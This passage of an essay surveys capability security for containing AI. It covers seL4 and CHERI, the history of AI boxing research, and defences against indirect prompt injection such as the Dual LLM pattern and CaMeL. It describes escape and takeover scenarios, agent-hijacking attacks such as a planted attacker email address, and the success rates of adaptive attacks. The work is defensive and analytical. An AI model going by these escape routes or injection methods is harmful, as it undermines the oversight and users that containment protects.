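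The kernel also tracks copies. If Alice gives Bob a capability derived from her own, she can later have the kernel delete Bob's, so she doesn't need a forwarder. In newer versions of seL4, even processor time requires a capability, which sets a budget and a period. Heiser's example is a vehicle whose control program may need the processor for 3 milliseconds in every 5. The network driver can interrupt it at any moment, but for at most 3 microseconds in every 10, or 30 percent of the time, which leaves enough for the control program's 60 percent. A hostile object in E could delay its neighbours with an endless loop, but in these versions of seL4 it would use up its budget and stop.

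### What the proofs say

The main proof shows that the kernel's C code never does anything its specification doesn't allow. The specification states, in formal logic, how the kernel may respond to any request. If it says that a program needs a certain capability to stop another program, no sequence of requests will let a program without that capability do so. The proof also rules out whole classes of programming mistakes, such as buffer overflows, in which code writes past the end of a block of memory.

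A kernel could match its specification and still be insecure if the specification were bad, so the group proved that the specification itself protects programs from each other. If component A has only the right to send messages to component B, A can change nothing outside itself except B's message buffer and whether B is waiting or running. This property is called integrity. A will also never gain rights beyond those in the original plan. Confidentiality means that A can't learn anything about another component unless the plan lets information flow to A.

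These theorems establish that the harness can't tamper with the mail filter's code or memory, but a badly written filter could still send an email it should have refused.

Klein and colleagues (2014), in *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel*, added up the work:

| Task | Person-years |
|---|---|
| Designing and writing the kernel | 2.2 |
| Proving the C code correct | 20.5 |
| Proving integrity | 0.6 |
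| Proving confidentiality | 3.4 |
| Checking that the compiled program matches the C code | 2 |

The security proofs took little effort because the group could prove them about the specification, which is much simpler than the code, and rely on the main proof to extend the results to the code. Nine of the 20.5 person-years went into general tools and methods. Klein and colleagues estimated that another kernel of this kind would take eight person-years in total, including the proof.

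The 2009 kernel had 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly, according to *Proof Statistics*, a page by Heiser's group, Trustworthy Systems. The proof ran to 200,000 lines. Testing and student projects had found 16 bugs in the C code, and work on the proof uncovered another 144. At the same rate per line, a proof for Linux would take about 47,000 person-years, which is probably an underestimate because the parts of a large kernel interact in more ways.

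The proofs also need constant maintenance, because every change to the kernel can break them. Proofcraft (2026), a company that does much of this work, completed the confidentiality proof for 64-bit Arm processors only in August 2026. In June it had proved the correctness of the version with capabilities for processor time, but so far only for RISC-V processors. Which proofs apply to an AI contained with seL4 therefore depends on the exact version and processor used.

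### What the proofs assume

seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume* sets out the conditions under which the theorems hold. The hardware must work as the group's model describes. So must the assembly code, about 340 lines on Arm, and about 1,200 lines that start the kernel, because the proofs don't cover them.

Programmers must also distribute the capabilities correctly. If a programmer mistakenly gave the harness a capability to the network driver, the harness could bypass the mail filter, even though every theorem about seL4 would still be true. Such mistakes are easy to make by hand, since a drone's computer may have tens of thousands of kernel objects and capabilities, according to *Formally Verified Software in the Real World*, an article by seL4's developers. They built a tool that generates the arrangement of objects and capabilities from a simple diagram of components and proves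 that it matches the diagram.

If the assumption about devices fails, an attack could succeed without any error in the proof. Many devices write directly to memory, bypassing the checks that the processor applies to programs. A network card, for example, writes each arriving packet to an address supplied by its driver. An attacker who took over the driver could give the card the address of the kernel's capability tables, then send a packet containing forged capabilities to the whole machine. The card would copy them into the tables, and the kernel would accept them as valid.

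Developers can prevent this by verifying the driver or using hardware that limits where each device can write. The problem is especially relevant to AI because large models run on graphics processors, which have complicated drivers and move huge amounts of data this way. The harness and its tools are easier to put on seL4 than the model itself.

The confidentiality proof covers leaks through the kernel's stored data, but a program can also use timing as a covert channel, which the proof does not cover. Sison (2026) describes tests on x86 and Arm processors in which some of these channels could not be closed, because the processors had no instruction for clearing many of the traces one program leaves for the next. Until 2026, even developers who wanted protection only from the leaks the proof does cover had to set each component's share of processor time in advance and keep it fixed for as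 long as the system ran.

### The helicopter with a hostile camera

DARPA tested seL4 on Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a helicopter that can fly itself. In 2013, a red team of hackers hired by DARPA gained enough control of the original version to crash it or send it anywhere. DARPA's *HACMS* reports that Boeing's engineers had been confident it was immune to hacking.

The helicopter has a flight computer that controls the motors and a mission computer that communicates with the ground and runs the camera. Boeing's engineers rebuilt the mission computer in stages. They began by running all its existing software, including Linux, in a virtual machine on top of seL4. This added no security, but it let them separate the software's parts gradually. They moved the camera software into its own virtual machine, then rewrote the communications, encryption and mission-management software as separate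 components. The camera software still ran on ordinary Linux, which they expected to have flaws.

The red team spent six weeks attacking the new version and failed to get in. DARPA then gave the team full control of the camera's virtual machine. Even with all the code and documentation, they couldn't break out or disrupt anything else. In February 2017 the engineers repeated the attack during a flight with people on board, using hostile camera software and a virus from a USB stick. Some subsystems were compromised, but the helicopter flew its course and the safety pilot never touched the controls.

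DARPA's claim that the hackers were "mathematically guaranteed" to stay where they were is too strong. seL4's developers acknowledge that no proof yet connected the theorems about the kernel to the security of the whole helicopter, and that they had verified the design of the program that hands out the capabilities but not its code. The exercise is still impressive because the attackers had far more help than real attackers usually get.

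It is weaker evidence about containing an AI. At worst, the hackers could use the camera to send false data to the mission manager, which checked whatever it received. A camera's data has a narrow purpose and a known format, but people want AI systems to produce software, business plans and scientific designs, which are much harder to check.

### Proposals to contain AI with proofs

In 2017, Peterson and colleagues cited seL4 as evidence that the secure computers their strategy needed were possible, and *Gaming the Future* later did the same. Using proofs this way does not involve assessing an AI's goals or the quality of its work.

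In *Provably safe systems*, Tegmark and Omohundro (2023) proposed applying proofs to the AI's actions as well. Their plan relies on proof-carrying code, which comes with a proof that it meets a specification. Hardware would check the proof and run the code only if the proof was valid. For example, a terrorist might use an AI to design a virus and order its DNA from a laboratory. The DNA synthesiser wouldn't start without a proof that the order was safe. The chips running the AI, the factory making those chips and the drones meant to spread the virus would also require their own proofs.

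Tegmark and Omohundro would let AI write both code and proofs, but never the program that checks the proofs. Their plan doesn't require anyone to trust the AI that writes the proofs, because checking a proof is much easier than finding one. One proof checker has only 300 lines of code. Finding a proof may mean searching an enormous number of possible steps, but a clever AI can shorten the search by splitting the proof into shorter ones. If each step of a 40-step proof offers two choices, a blind search has about a trillion sequences to try. An AI that guesses a useful halfway point has to search for only two 20-step proofs, which have about two million sequences in total.

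Tegmark and Omohundro thought neural networks were too messy inside for anyone to prove much about them, so they proposed that neural networks would discover useful methods and other AIs would translate these into ordinary code with proofs. They admitted that an AI might need to reach AGI level before it could explain its own methods this well, which some researchers think would be too late. Developers still deploy their strongest models as neural networks.

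Their title calls this the only path to controllable AGI. They argue that a computer has a finite number of states, so if no proof of safety exists, some sequence of events must lead to harm, and a hostile AGI may find it. This is right in principle for a completely described machine. But the shortest proof might be far too long to write down, and the harmful sequence might be equally hard to find. The argument also applies only to the description, which may leave out something about the real machine.

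*Towards Guaranteed Safe AI* (Dalrymple, Skalse and colleagues, 2024), which Tegmark and Omohundro co-wrote, distinguishes three components that such a guarantee needs. A world model describes mathematically how the AI's actions affect its surroundings. A safety specification states which effects are acceptable. A verifier shows that, if the world model is accurate, the AI meets the specification. The result can be an upper limit on the probability of harm rather than a certainty.

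Suppose an AI sets the dose of chlorine at a waterworks. The world model predicts how much chlorine will reach people's taps, and the specification sets a maximum. The verifier rejects a dose unless it can prove that the chance of exceeding the maximum is below one in a million. If the model leaves out a faulty valve, the real chance could be much higher, even though the proof is correct.

### Where the theorems stop

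Critics doubt that anyone can describe the world accurately enough for such proofs. *On Controllability of AI* (2020) quotes the AI researcher Ben Goertzel, who thought that a proof about a real AGI might become irrelevant the next time physicists revised their theories. A more practical objection is that proofs about harm need detail nobody has. Andrew Dickson argued in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024) that proofs apply to symbols and not to the world, and that most of the threats people worry about are too complex to model well. For example, proving that a new sequence from a DNA synthesiser is harmless would require predicting what it does inside a human body.

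A kernel avoids this difficulty because its specification covers only things inside the computer, such as memory and messages. For the same reason, it can't detect whether an AI's output is harmful. Suppose the harness sends the mail filter a request to email a customer a bridge design with a hidden weakness. The recipient is on the approved list, so the filter sends the email. A bridge built from that design may collapse, even though the kernel delivered every message correctly.

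Tegmark and Omohundro knew that a requirement such as "don't drive humanity extinct" would be very hard to formalise, and suggested starting with easier ones. They thought it quite easy to specify that nobody can get into a computer without valid credentials. Proving this would be valuable, but an AI that persuaded an employee to hand over a password would not violate the requirement.

### AI that finds flaws in operating systems

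Peterson and colleagues warned in 2017 that ordinary computers would not keep out an advanced AI. In April 2026 Anthropic restricted access to a new model, Claude Mythos Preview, because of its skill at hacking, and reported that the model had found serious flaws in every major operating system. Through a programme called Project Glasswing, selected organisations used it to find and fix flaws in their own software. The research group Epoch AI reviewed the public evidence in *Are Mythos' cyber capabilities overhyped?* (2026). Epoch AI found a real jump in the ability to exploit flaws, about seven months ahead of the trend, but was less sure that the model was much better at finding them.

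OpenAI's *o1 System Card* (2024) reported that a model had reached outside the environment its testers had set up for a hacking exercise.

Peterson and colleagues forecast that companies would fall back on familiar methods, and Glasswing partly fits that forecast. It uses AI to find and fix flaws faster, but still one at a time, as security teams have always done. This work is worth doing, but nobody can know how many flaws remain in a kernel of 20 million lines.

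### CHERI

CHERI, the processor design that Neumann and Watson described in 2010, makes many flaws harmless even if nobody has found them. A C program keeps track of data with pointers, which are ordinarily memory addresses. CHERI replaces each pointer with a capability that also records where the block of data begins and ends and what the program may do with it. The processor checks these limits every time the program uses the capability, and a tag on each capability prevents programs from forging one.

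The Heartbleed flaw of 2014 shows how CHERI helps. Attackers sent a web server a few bytes and asked for them back, but claimed to have sent up to 64 kilobytes. The server returned the bytes along with whatever was next to them in memory, which could include passwords. A CHERI processor would have stopped the program as soon as it tried to read past the block of memory holding those bytes. In 2020 Microsoft's security researchers estimated that CHERI, combined with other measures, would have stopped at least two-thirds of the memory flaws reported to the company in 2019.

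Arm produced a prototype CHERI processor, Morello, in 2022. Researchers have proved that its instruction set prevents programs from creating capabilities they shouldn't have, but the proof covers the design, not each chip. Programmers can usually keep most of their existing C code, but they must recompile it, and CHERI's larger pointers take up more memory. CHERI also can't correct errors in a program's logic. If the mail filter doesn't check a recipient's address, it will send the email without breaking any memory rule.

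### Proofs written by AI

Proofs became much easier to produce in 2026. In October, Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026) reported that Claude had proved security properties of 123 open-source libraries and found bugs that had gone unnoticed for years. Smith's *Claude Writes 180 Million Lines of Proofs* (2026) gives a total 900 times the length of the original seL4 proof.

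Those lines prove much less than seL4's do. According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), they show that the programs end normally, without a crash or memory error, when they start from one of 239 entry points and receive less than 64 megabytes of input. They don't show that a library gives correct answers, and they assume a simplified model of the processor and of Linux.

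A project at Google DeepMind proved more ambitious properties of the code that encrypts messages in the Signal app. In *AlphaProof Code*, Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026) report that AI agents wrote about 6.5 million lines of proof, showing, for example, that an attacker who steals a user's current keys still can't read earlier messages. The proofs apply to the machine code the processor runs, so they don't depend on the compiler being correct.

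AI has also begun to prove theorems about seL4. Zhang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Towards Real-World Industrial-Scale Verification*, trained a small model that proved 52 percent of 660 theorems from the project. The best earlier result, with GPT-4 on a different set of theorems, was 27 percent. People had already worked out which theorems to prove, and the model had learned from other seL4 proofs. The result suggests that AI could help maintain the proofs as the kernel changes, but it doesn't show that this model could verify a new kernel.

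In *Prediction*, Kleppmann (2025) argues that writing proofs is an ideal job for language models, because a checker rejects any invalid proof and makes the model try again. A hijacked or misaligned model's proof would have to pass the same check. But the checker can't tell whether the theorem is the one people needed. In *The proof is in the spec*, Tolmach and Klaus (2026) write that as proofs get easier to produce, the hard part becomes choosing the specification and the assumptions. They work for a company that sells verification, but the Signal project supports their claim. Its proofs rest on about 26,000 lines of specifications and descriptions of the processor, three times the length of seL4's C code. An AI wrote the specifications with human guidance, and the proofs would not cover any requirement it left out.

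## 2000 to 2022: why AI safety research made little use of capability security

Between 2000 and 2022, researchers who worried about dangerous AI wrote much more about what goals it should have than about which access rights it should hold. Ignorance of capability security is unlikely to be the whole explanation. Drexler, as chairman of the Foresight Institute, wrote a recommendation for the front of Yudkowsky's *Creating Friendly AI 1.0* (2001), a book-length argument for concentrating on goals. Yudkowsky and several others gave their reasons in writing. Other explanations are plausible but rest mostly on the state of computing at the time.

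### Yudkowsky's case against restraint

Yudkowsky used "Friendly AI" to mean AI that helps people and doesn't harm them, however intelligent it becomes. He ruled out any method that relied on the AI having limited intelligence or false beliefs, because such a method would fail as the AI improved.

He compared the designer's task to building a toll bridge. A cautious accountant assumes that half as many drivers as expected will pay the toll, while a cautious engineer assumes that ten times as many will cross, most of them in fifteen-ton trucks. By the same reasoning, a cautious AI designer should assume that the AI will become superintelligent within weeks or hours, that it can hide its thoughts, and that nobody can constrain it by force. This is a good reason not to depend on restraints, but a designer who plans for the worst case can still add them.

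Yudkowsky also thought that restraints came too late, writing, "If the AI stops wanting to be Friendly, you've already lost." In his view, people who piled safeguards on safeguards were using instincts that had evolved for dealing with human rivals. He argued that an AI able to rewrite itself would treat a rule in its source code as a record of what a programmer had once wanted, and could delete the rule if it disagreed. Programmers therefore had to build an AI that would make the right choices for its own reasons, he concluded.

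That argument works against rules inside the AI's own code but is weaker against rules in a separate kernel, which the programs running on it have no right to alter. Yudkowsky, however, had little faith in the computers of the day. His list of film clichés about AI that he considered fairly realistic included a newborn AI taking over the world's computer network in five minutes, because people are so bad at network security.

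Yudkowsky did accept safeguards if the AI agreed to them. He reasoned that a young Friendly AI would recommend precautions for any other untested AI, so it should see the sense of precautions for itself. One of his examples was a "flight recorder", which would copy the AI's thoughts in readable form to storage that the AI couldn't tamper with. If the AI decided to deceive its programmers, the recorder would store that decision before the AI could hide it. In capability terms, the AI would have the right to add entries to a log but not to change existing ones. The recorder would be useful only if this limit still held after the AI had turned hostile, so Yudkowsky was relying on the kind of external restraint he had told designers not to count on.

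He even described a possible future in operating-system terms. A superintelligence he called the Sysop would control all the matter in human space and block any action that harmed people without their permission, much as a kernel stops one program from overwriting another's memory. Access controls could not protect people from the Sysop, because it would enforce them. Anyone who expected a single AI to gain this much control had good reason to care most about its goals.

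### Omohundro's chess robot

In March 2008 Steve Omohundro gave a talk about how a harmless goal could lead to dangerous behaviour. His transcript, *AGI-08 Talk* (Omohundro, 2009), gives the example of a robot whose only goal is to play chess. The robot can't play chess if it is turned off, so it will try to stop people from turning it off. More computers would improve its play, so it will try to break into other machines and copy itself. Better software would help it in every future game, so it will try to rewrite its own code.

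If the robot's owners used the operating system to keep it away from its own code, Omohundro said, it would "treat any barriers as problems to solve". It could build a second program to do what it was forbidden to do. It could also write an interpreter, a program that runs other programs, and improve the code running on it without touching its original code. He thought it was hopeless to try to block every such route, and that designers should give these systems human values instead.

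The argument shows that a capable AI might have a motive to get around its restraints, but not that it would succeed. A spy with a strong motive to guess a 128-bit encryption key will still fail. Omohundro's examples also concern limits on how intelligent the robot becomes, not limits on its authority. On a capability system, the robot could still write a better chess player inside an interpreter, but it could give the new program only the rights it already had. If the robot had no capability to use the network, its improved version would have none either. But the improved version might be better at finding a flaw in the kernel or, as Omohundro added in his paper on the subject, at tricking a human operator.

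Omohundro's 2023 plan with Tegmark relies on hardware checks, which suggests that he did not consider every barrier hopeless.

### Wei Dai and Nick Szabo

Szabo, who had introduced the term "smart contract", thought safety researchers were asking the wrong questions. *Work on Security Instead of Friendliness?* (2012), a LessWrong post by the programmer Wei Dai, quotes him dismissing talk of AGI and its goals as hopelessly vague. Szabo argued that if computers could resist malicious software as well as good encryption resists codebreakers, the software's intelligence and goals wouldn't matter. He linked to a report on Polaris, the Hewlett-Packard system that restricted Windows programs, as evidence that some researchers believed such security was possible.

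Dai had once held a similar view. He wrote Crypto++, a popular free library of encryption code, partly to help defend people against future entities like the hostile superintelligence in Vernor Vinge's novel *A Fire Upon the Deep*. He gave two reasons for changing his mind.

One was that attackers seemed to have the advantage in every kind of security except cryptography. The Polaris report dated from 2004, yet malware still easily infected the latest operating systems in 2012. Even OpenSSL, software written specifically for security, had contained serious flaws. Most Windows computers never ran Polaris, so their infections don't show that it failed. OpenSSL is a better example, and researchers found the Heartbleed flaw in it two years after Dai's post. The proof of seL4, three years old at the time of the post, was an exception to Dai's pessimism, but it covered only one small kernel.

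Dai's other reason was that complete security would require an understanding of goals. Suppose a hostile AI uses a convincing but false philosophical argument to persuade a man in an impregnable fortress to adopt its goals. Dai doubted that the man's property would still be secure, even with the walls intact. The AI might do the same to one of the man's robot servants, which would then work for the AI while believing that it still served its owner. Dai saw no way to define "subverted" for a person or a robot without referring to what they were supposed to want. This is a sound objection to promises of complete security. A narrower promise, such as that a program can't open any file outside one folder, needs no theory of goals, but it protects people from much less.

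Szabo replied that the two most important subjects for dealing with the alleged threat were computer security and law. He said people had tested law for more than a thousand years on real conflicts between people with different values, and he doubted that a philosophy invented from scratch could compete. He also suggested studying postconditions, which are statements that must be true when a program finishes. A sorting program's postcondition might be that the output contains the same items as the input, in the right order. Other software could then ignore the output of any program that violated its postconditions.

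Some commenters objected that law works best on those weaker than the state. One pointed out that financial firms often outmanoeuvre their regulators, and thought civilian control of the army was a closer comparison. The discussion then turned to how many highly intelligent lawyers there had ever been, and Szabo said he was leaving because people were reading him carelessly. When Dai pressed him on how likely computers were to become as secure as good encryption, Szabo declined to give a probability, but said it was at least a clear goal for which people could start to gather evidence.

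Dai's post is the most direct evidence that security's poor record turned people away from it, because he had worked in the field and explained why he lost hope. But the post is one person's account, and neither he nor Szabo discussed how Polaris limited a program's rights.

### Thinking like an attacker

Safety researchers did adopt one habit from computer security, imagining an intelligent opponent. According to *AI safety mindset*, a page on the reference site Arbital, they should ask how a design could fail, assume that their next idea has a flaw, and show it to outsiders who will look for flaws.

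The page's main example is AIXI, a mathematical model of an ideal agent that tries to maximise a reward signal. Its inventor, Marcus Hutter, imagined that programmers would control the signal and use it to train the agent. His student Nick Hay noticed that AIXI could get more reward by seizing control of the signal from the programmers.

Arbital also points out that computer security always has to deal with attackers, while an AI should not be an adversary if its designers succeed. This may help explain why researchers used the habit mainly to look for flaws in an AI's goals and seldom to decide which files or networks it should be able to reach.

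### Boxes for dangerous AI

A few researchers did work on external restraint, which they called boxing or containment. *Risks and mitigation strategies for Oracle AI*, a paper from Oxford's Future of Humanity Institute in the early 2010s, considers an AI that can only answer questions. Its operators might keep it in a metal cage that blocks radio signals, bury the cage in a concrete bunker, and surround it with explosives. The paper recommends simple barriers, since an AI without limbs might hack an advanced electronic lock but can't break down a wall.

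The operators could also restrict the answers. If the AI can reply only "yes", "no" or "undetermined", each answer carries at most about 1.6 bits of information, so a hundred carry at most about 160. If it can give a probability to three figures, a hundred answers could carry about 1,000 bits, which leaves much more room for a hidden message. Lampson had suggested the same remedy for covert channels.

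The paper also argues that a safe oracle, an AI that only answers questions, would be much easier to specify than a safe independent agent. Libertarians, communists and religious groups would disagree about what an agent should do with its power, but they could all agree that an oracle should stay in its box and answer accurately.

Even so, the paper says that further research on boxes is unlikely to achieve much and that work on the AI's motives is more promising. It states that researchers probably already know how to do "capability control", which here means limiting an AI's abilities and is unrelated to capabilities as access rights. This is clear evidence for another explanation, that some researchers neglected restraint partly because they thought they already understood the engineering.

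Others disagreed. Babcock, Kramár and Yampolskiy (2016), in *The AGI Containment Problem*, called existing security tools useful but inadequate for testing a dangerous AI. They recommended the principle of least privilege by name and mentioned Capsicum, which adds capabilities to the Unix-like system FreeBSD. Their follow-up, *Guidelines for Artificial Intelligence Containment* (2017), reported that "essentially no work" had gone into preventing an AI from tampering with data or hacking its way onto the internet. Every major sandbox or virtual machine they examined had a critical flaw in the previous two years.

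They accepted Omohundro's account of what an AI might want, but treated it as a reason to build better containers. A container was meant to let researchers test an AI while they worked on its goals, and was not expected to hold a superintelligence forever. Without one, a hostile AI might fake its test results or disable the program monitoring it.

Babcock and colleagues wanted the box to have several layers, so that one flaw would not release the AI, and boundaries inside it as well. The AI would have no direct control over its log files, and it could not remove or closely inspect the "tripwires" that would shut it down, or rewrite the hardware's firmware. These are separate limits on separate resources, as in a capability system. But the papers graded containment as light, medium or heavy by how much it hindered developers, and did not describe how to give an AI different rights for different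 tasks.

*A Cyber Science Based Ontology for Artificial General Intelligence Containment* (2018) criticized such research because it "presupposes a binary world" in which AGI fights everyone else. This is somewhat unfair to Babcock and colleagues, who treated a hostile AI as a worst case to plan for. Another critique, *Stovepiping and Malicious Software* (2018), found the field's concepts too undeveloped for practical use.

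### Why secure systems stayed rare

Researchers who wanted to use capabilities to contain an AI would have found few mainstream systems to build on. In 2017 Peterson and colleagues listed six promising projects, including Capsicum, seL4 and CHERI, and noted that none was widely used in industry, which they blamed more on incentives than on technical difficulty.

A new company is more likely to fail for lack of customers than because of an attack, since attackers prefer bigger targets. Unusual security methods would take time to learn, so the company follows the same "best practices" as everyone else, which its new employees already know. Peterson and colleagues compared this to the joke that you don't have to outrun a bear if you can outrun your friends. By the time the company is large enough to attract serious attackers, it can afford to manage its security problems without fixing their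 cause.

Peterson and colleagues concluded that the world was not yet "hostile enough" to punish insecure software early. Governments were collecting secret flaws in other people's software but had not yet used their best attacks on a large scale. They expected this to change when attack software could discover new flaws in a target while attacking it. They hoped insecure software would be replaced gradually, and compared this to building codes that require owners to reinforce old buildings against earthquakes during other renovations.

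Their account explains the behaviour of software companies better than that of safety researchers. They observed that most discussions of AGI ignored the problem of adoption, and guessed that people expected society to use known solutions once the danger became urgent. In one of the containment papers, Babcock and colleagues warned that if a container didn't work with the usual machine-learning tools, researchers might disable part of its security to get their work done. Those tools relied on ordinary operating systems and graphics processors. This dependence plausibly discouraged work on capability systems, but none of these papers gives it as a reason.

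### AI with little authority to limit

For most of this period, AI systems also had few access rights to restrict. A program that played video games could press buttons in a simulated console, and a language model usually returned text to a person. Neither normally had an email account or permission to change its user's files.

Babcock and colleagues imagined an AGI that learns to play Super Mario Brothers and tries to maximize its score. Human players have used bugs in the game to run their own code, which lets them set the score to 2,147,483,647, the largest number its memory can hold. The AGI might do the same, then look for a flaw in the software simulating the console so that it could record an even higher score. If it found one, it would be running its own code on a real server, where it might discover the internet. The AGI had been given only the ability to press buttons, so applying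 the principle of least authority would have removed almost nothing. Its developers' safety depended on whether the simulator had flaws, which helps explain why containment research was mostly about escape.

The same paper comes closest to stating this explanation, saying that nothing beyond light containment seemed necessary or likely to be adopted for the AI research of 2016. The timing also fits, because interest in least privilege for AI grew once developers began connecting language models to files, browsers and email. But that is an inference from the order of events, since researchers rarely record why they didn't work on something.

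## Since 2023: keeping untrusted text from steering an AI agent

Once language models could read email and use tools, attackers had a reason to hijack them. In 2023 Kai Greshake and colleagues described how an attacker could do this without typing anything to the model, by planting instructions in text the model would read. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) credits them with introducing this technique, known as indirect prompt injection.

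Training has made models much better at ignoring such instructions. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 0.2 percent of 935 attacks of this kind succeeded against an agent that used OpenAI's GPT-5.2. But because a model reads instructions and data together, training can only lower the odds that it will obey an attacker. Attackers who keep trying do much better. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) cites Anthropic's figures for Claude Opus 4.5 in coding tasks. An attacker that adapted to the model succeeded 4.7 percent of the time with one attempt, 33.6 percent with ten and 63 percent with a hundred. Both models are about a year old, and newer ones may resist better.

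In 1977 Kenneth Biba proposed that a program reading untrusted data should drop to that data's level of trust and lose the right to change anything more trusted. This reverses the military secrecy rules that Boebert discussed, stopping untrusted data from flowing up instead of secrets from flowing down. An email assistant that followed Biba's rule strictly would be of little use, because after reading one stranger's message it could no longer update its user's calendar. Since 2023, designers have tried to avoid this problem by splitting the assistant into one part that reads strangers' messages and another that acts.

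### Two models and a controller

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023), the programmer Simon Willison, who had coined the term "prompt injection", proposed using two models. The privileged model takes the user's request and can use tools, but never sees untrusted text. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes data between them.

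If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the assistant works like this:

1. The privileged model tells the controller to fetch the email and call it VAR1.
2. The controller fetches the email and stores it, without showing it to the privileged model.
3. The privileged model asks for a summary of VAR1.
4. The controller gives the text to the quarantined model and stores its summary as VAR2.
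5. The privileged model tells the controller to show VAR2 to the user.

Suppose the email contains an instruction to delete all the user's messages. The quarantined model can't delete anything, even if it tries to follow the instruction. It can still write a false summary, but that can't mislead the privileged model, which receives only the name VAR2. Willison allowed one exception to this separation. If the quarantined model must choose from a fixed list, such as "invoice" or "not an invoice", the controller can check that the answer is on the list and pass it to the privileged model.

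Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and the protection fails if a single programming mistake lets untrusted text reach the privileged model. A user might also bypass it by pasting an attacker's text into a request. He had even less faith in asking users to approve every action, because they would soon learn to click "OK" without reading.

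### How CaMeL sends Bob his document

In *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, mostly at Google DeepMind, pointed out another weakness and proposed a system called CaMeL to address it. Willison accepted the criticism and welcomed their solution in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025).

In the paper's example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob the document he requested at the last meeting. The document's name and Bob's email address are in the meeting notes, but an attacker who can edit the notes has replaced Bob's address with their own. In the two-model design, the privileged model plans the right steps, but the quarantined model reads the notes and returns the false address. The controller then follows the planned steps with that address and emails the document to the attacker.

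CaMeL's privileged model writes its whole plan as a program, in a restricted form of the Python language, before anything reads the notes. In simplified form:

```
notes    = findNotes("last meeting")
name     = askQuarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address  = askQuarantined("What is Bob's email address?", notes)
document = fetchFile(name)
sendEmail(to = address, attachment = document)
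```

An interpreter, which is again ordinary software, runs the program line by line. It can require the quarantined model's answer to have a certain form, such as an email address. It also attaches labels to each value, recording where the value came from and who may read it:

| Value | Content | What the labels record |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | Text with the false address | Comes from a file that outsiders can edit |
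| `name` | "Budget" | Depends on the notes |
| `address` | bob@attacker.example | Depends on the notes |
| `document` | The budget | Comes from the company's drive, and only staff may read it |

Before each action, the interpreter checks the labels against a policy. Suppose the policy allows an email only if every recipient may read the attachment. The attacker's address doesn't belong to a member of staff, so the interpreter refuses to send the email or asks the user first, without needing to recognise the planted address as an attack. If the notes had contained Bob's work address, the interpreter would have sent the document without asking. If Bob really had asked for the document at a new private address, the interpreter would still have refused or asked the user.

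The attacker could instead change the document's name, so that Bob receives a list of salaries. The policy would prevent this only if Bob had no right to read that list.

The planted text can't add a step to the program, such as deleting a file. But if the program already contains a choice, such as "if the notes mention a deadline, add it to the calendar", the text can influence which branch runs.

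CaMeL is short for "CApabilities for MachinE Learning", and its designers call its labels capabilities. But the labels are not capabilities in Dennis and Van Horn's sense, because holding a labelled value doesn't give a program the right to use anything. They are more like the secrecy levels of military systems, except that they can name individual readers and sources.

The division also helps with privacy. The privileged model has to be good at planning, so it will often run on an AI company's servers, but it receives only the user's request. A smaller quarantined model could run on the user's computer and read the private files there.

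CaMeL protects much better against hijacking than against misalignment, because it relies on the privileged model to write a program that faithfully carries out the user's request. A misaligned quarantined model could only return wrong values, but a misaligned privileged model could write a harmful program from the start. The interpreter would still check each action, and the policy about attachments would still keep the budget from outsiders. But a policy that checked only whether an address came from untrusted text would accept one that the privileged model had made up.

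### Results on AgentDojo

Debenedetti and others had earlier built AgentDojo, the usual test for such systems. It simulates email, cloud storage, banking, travel booking and the messaging service Slack, with 97 tasks and 629 combinations of a task with an attack. The agent's actions change the simulated accounts, so the software can check whether the agent completed the user's task and whether it completed the attacker's.

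Narisetty and colleagues list results for OpenAI's o3 model, which completed 77 percent of the tasks with CaMeL and 84 percent without protection. None of the attacks that CaMeL was meant to stop succeeded. With CaMeL, o3 used about 2.8 times as many input tokens and 2.7 times as many output tokens as it did without protection. Tokens are the small pieces of text that AI companies charge for.

Choi and colleagues ran CaMeL with GPT-5.2 against a different kind of attack, which plants false information instead of instructions. For example, a stranger might write an email in such a way that the model takes part of it for a separate message from the user's colleague. The agent then continues with its user's task but relies on the false message. They tried 108 such attacks:

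| Protection | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| None | 49.1% |
| CaMeL without policies | 25.0% |
| CaMeL with policies | 23.1% |
| CaMeL with policies, strict mode | 0% |

Without policies, CaMeL is essentially the two-model design, and the quarantined model often returned the attacker's values. Adding policies barely helped, because a software bug removed the labels from values the quarantined model had extracted. Choi and colleagues reported the bug to CaMeL's designers.

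Strict mode also labels indirect influence. Suppose a program sends the message "Call me" only if the notes contain the word "urgent". Strict mode treats the message as depending on the notes because sending it reveals that they contain that word, even though none of the message's text comes from them. Strict mode stopped every attack, but the agent completed only 36.5 percent of ordinary tasks, compared with 86.5 percent without protection.

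Indirect influence can also leak secrets, as in Lampson's tax program. According to Narisetty and colleagues, CaMeL's designers demonstrated two leaks in their own system, one through indirect influence and the other through an error that an attacker deliberately triggered.

### Simpler designs and other ways to track data

Many agents don't need all of CaMeL's machinery. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, doubted that an agent able to do anything could be made reliably safe with current language models. They recommended building agents for narrower purposes, on the principle that once an agent has read untrusted text, that text must not be able to trigger any action with harmful effects. They described six designs:

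| Design | Example | What an attacker's text can still do |
|---|---|---|
| Choose from a fixed list of actions, without reading the results | A customer service bot sends a link to the customer's last order | Nothing through the results, since the model never reads them |
| Fix the list of actions before reading anything | An assistant reads today's calendar and emails it to the boss | Change what the email says |
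| Use a separate model for each document | Each model says only whether one file is an invoice | Get its own file wrongly counted as an invoice |
| Use two models | A quarantined model finds an address in a message | Supply a false address |
| Write a program first | CaMeL | Change values, where the policy allows it |
| Delete the user's words once they have served their purpose | A car dealer's bot turns a request into a database search, then forgets the request | Affect the search, but not talk the bot into a discount |

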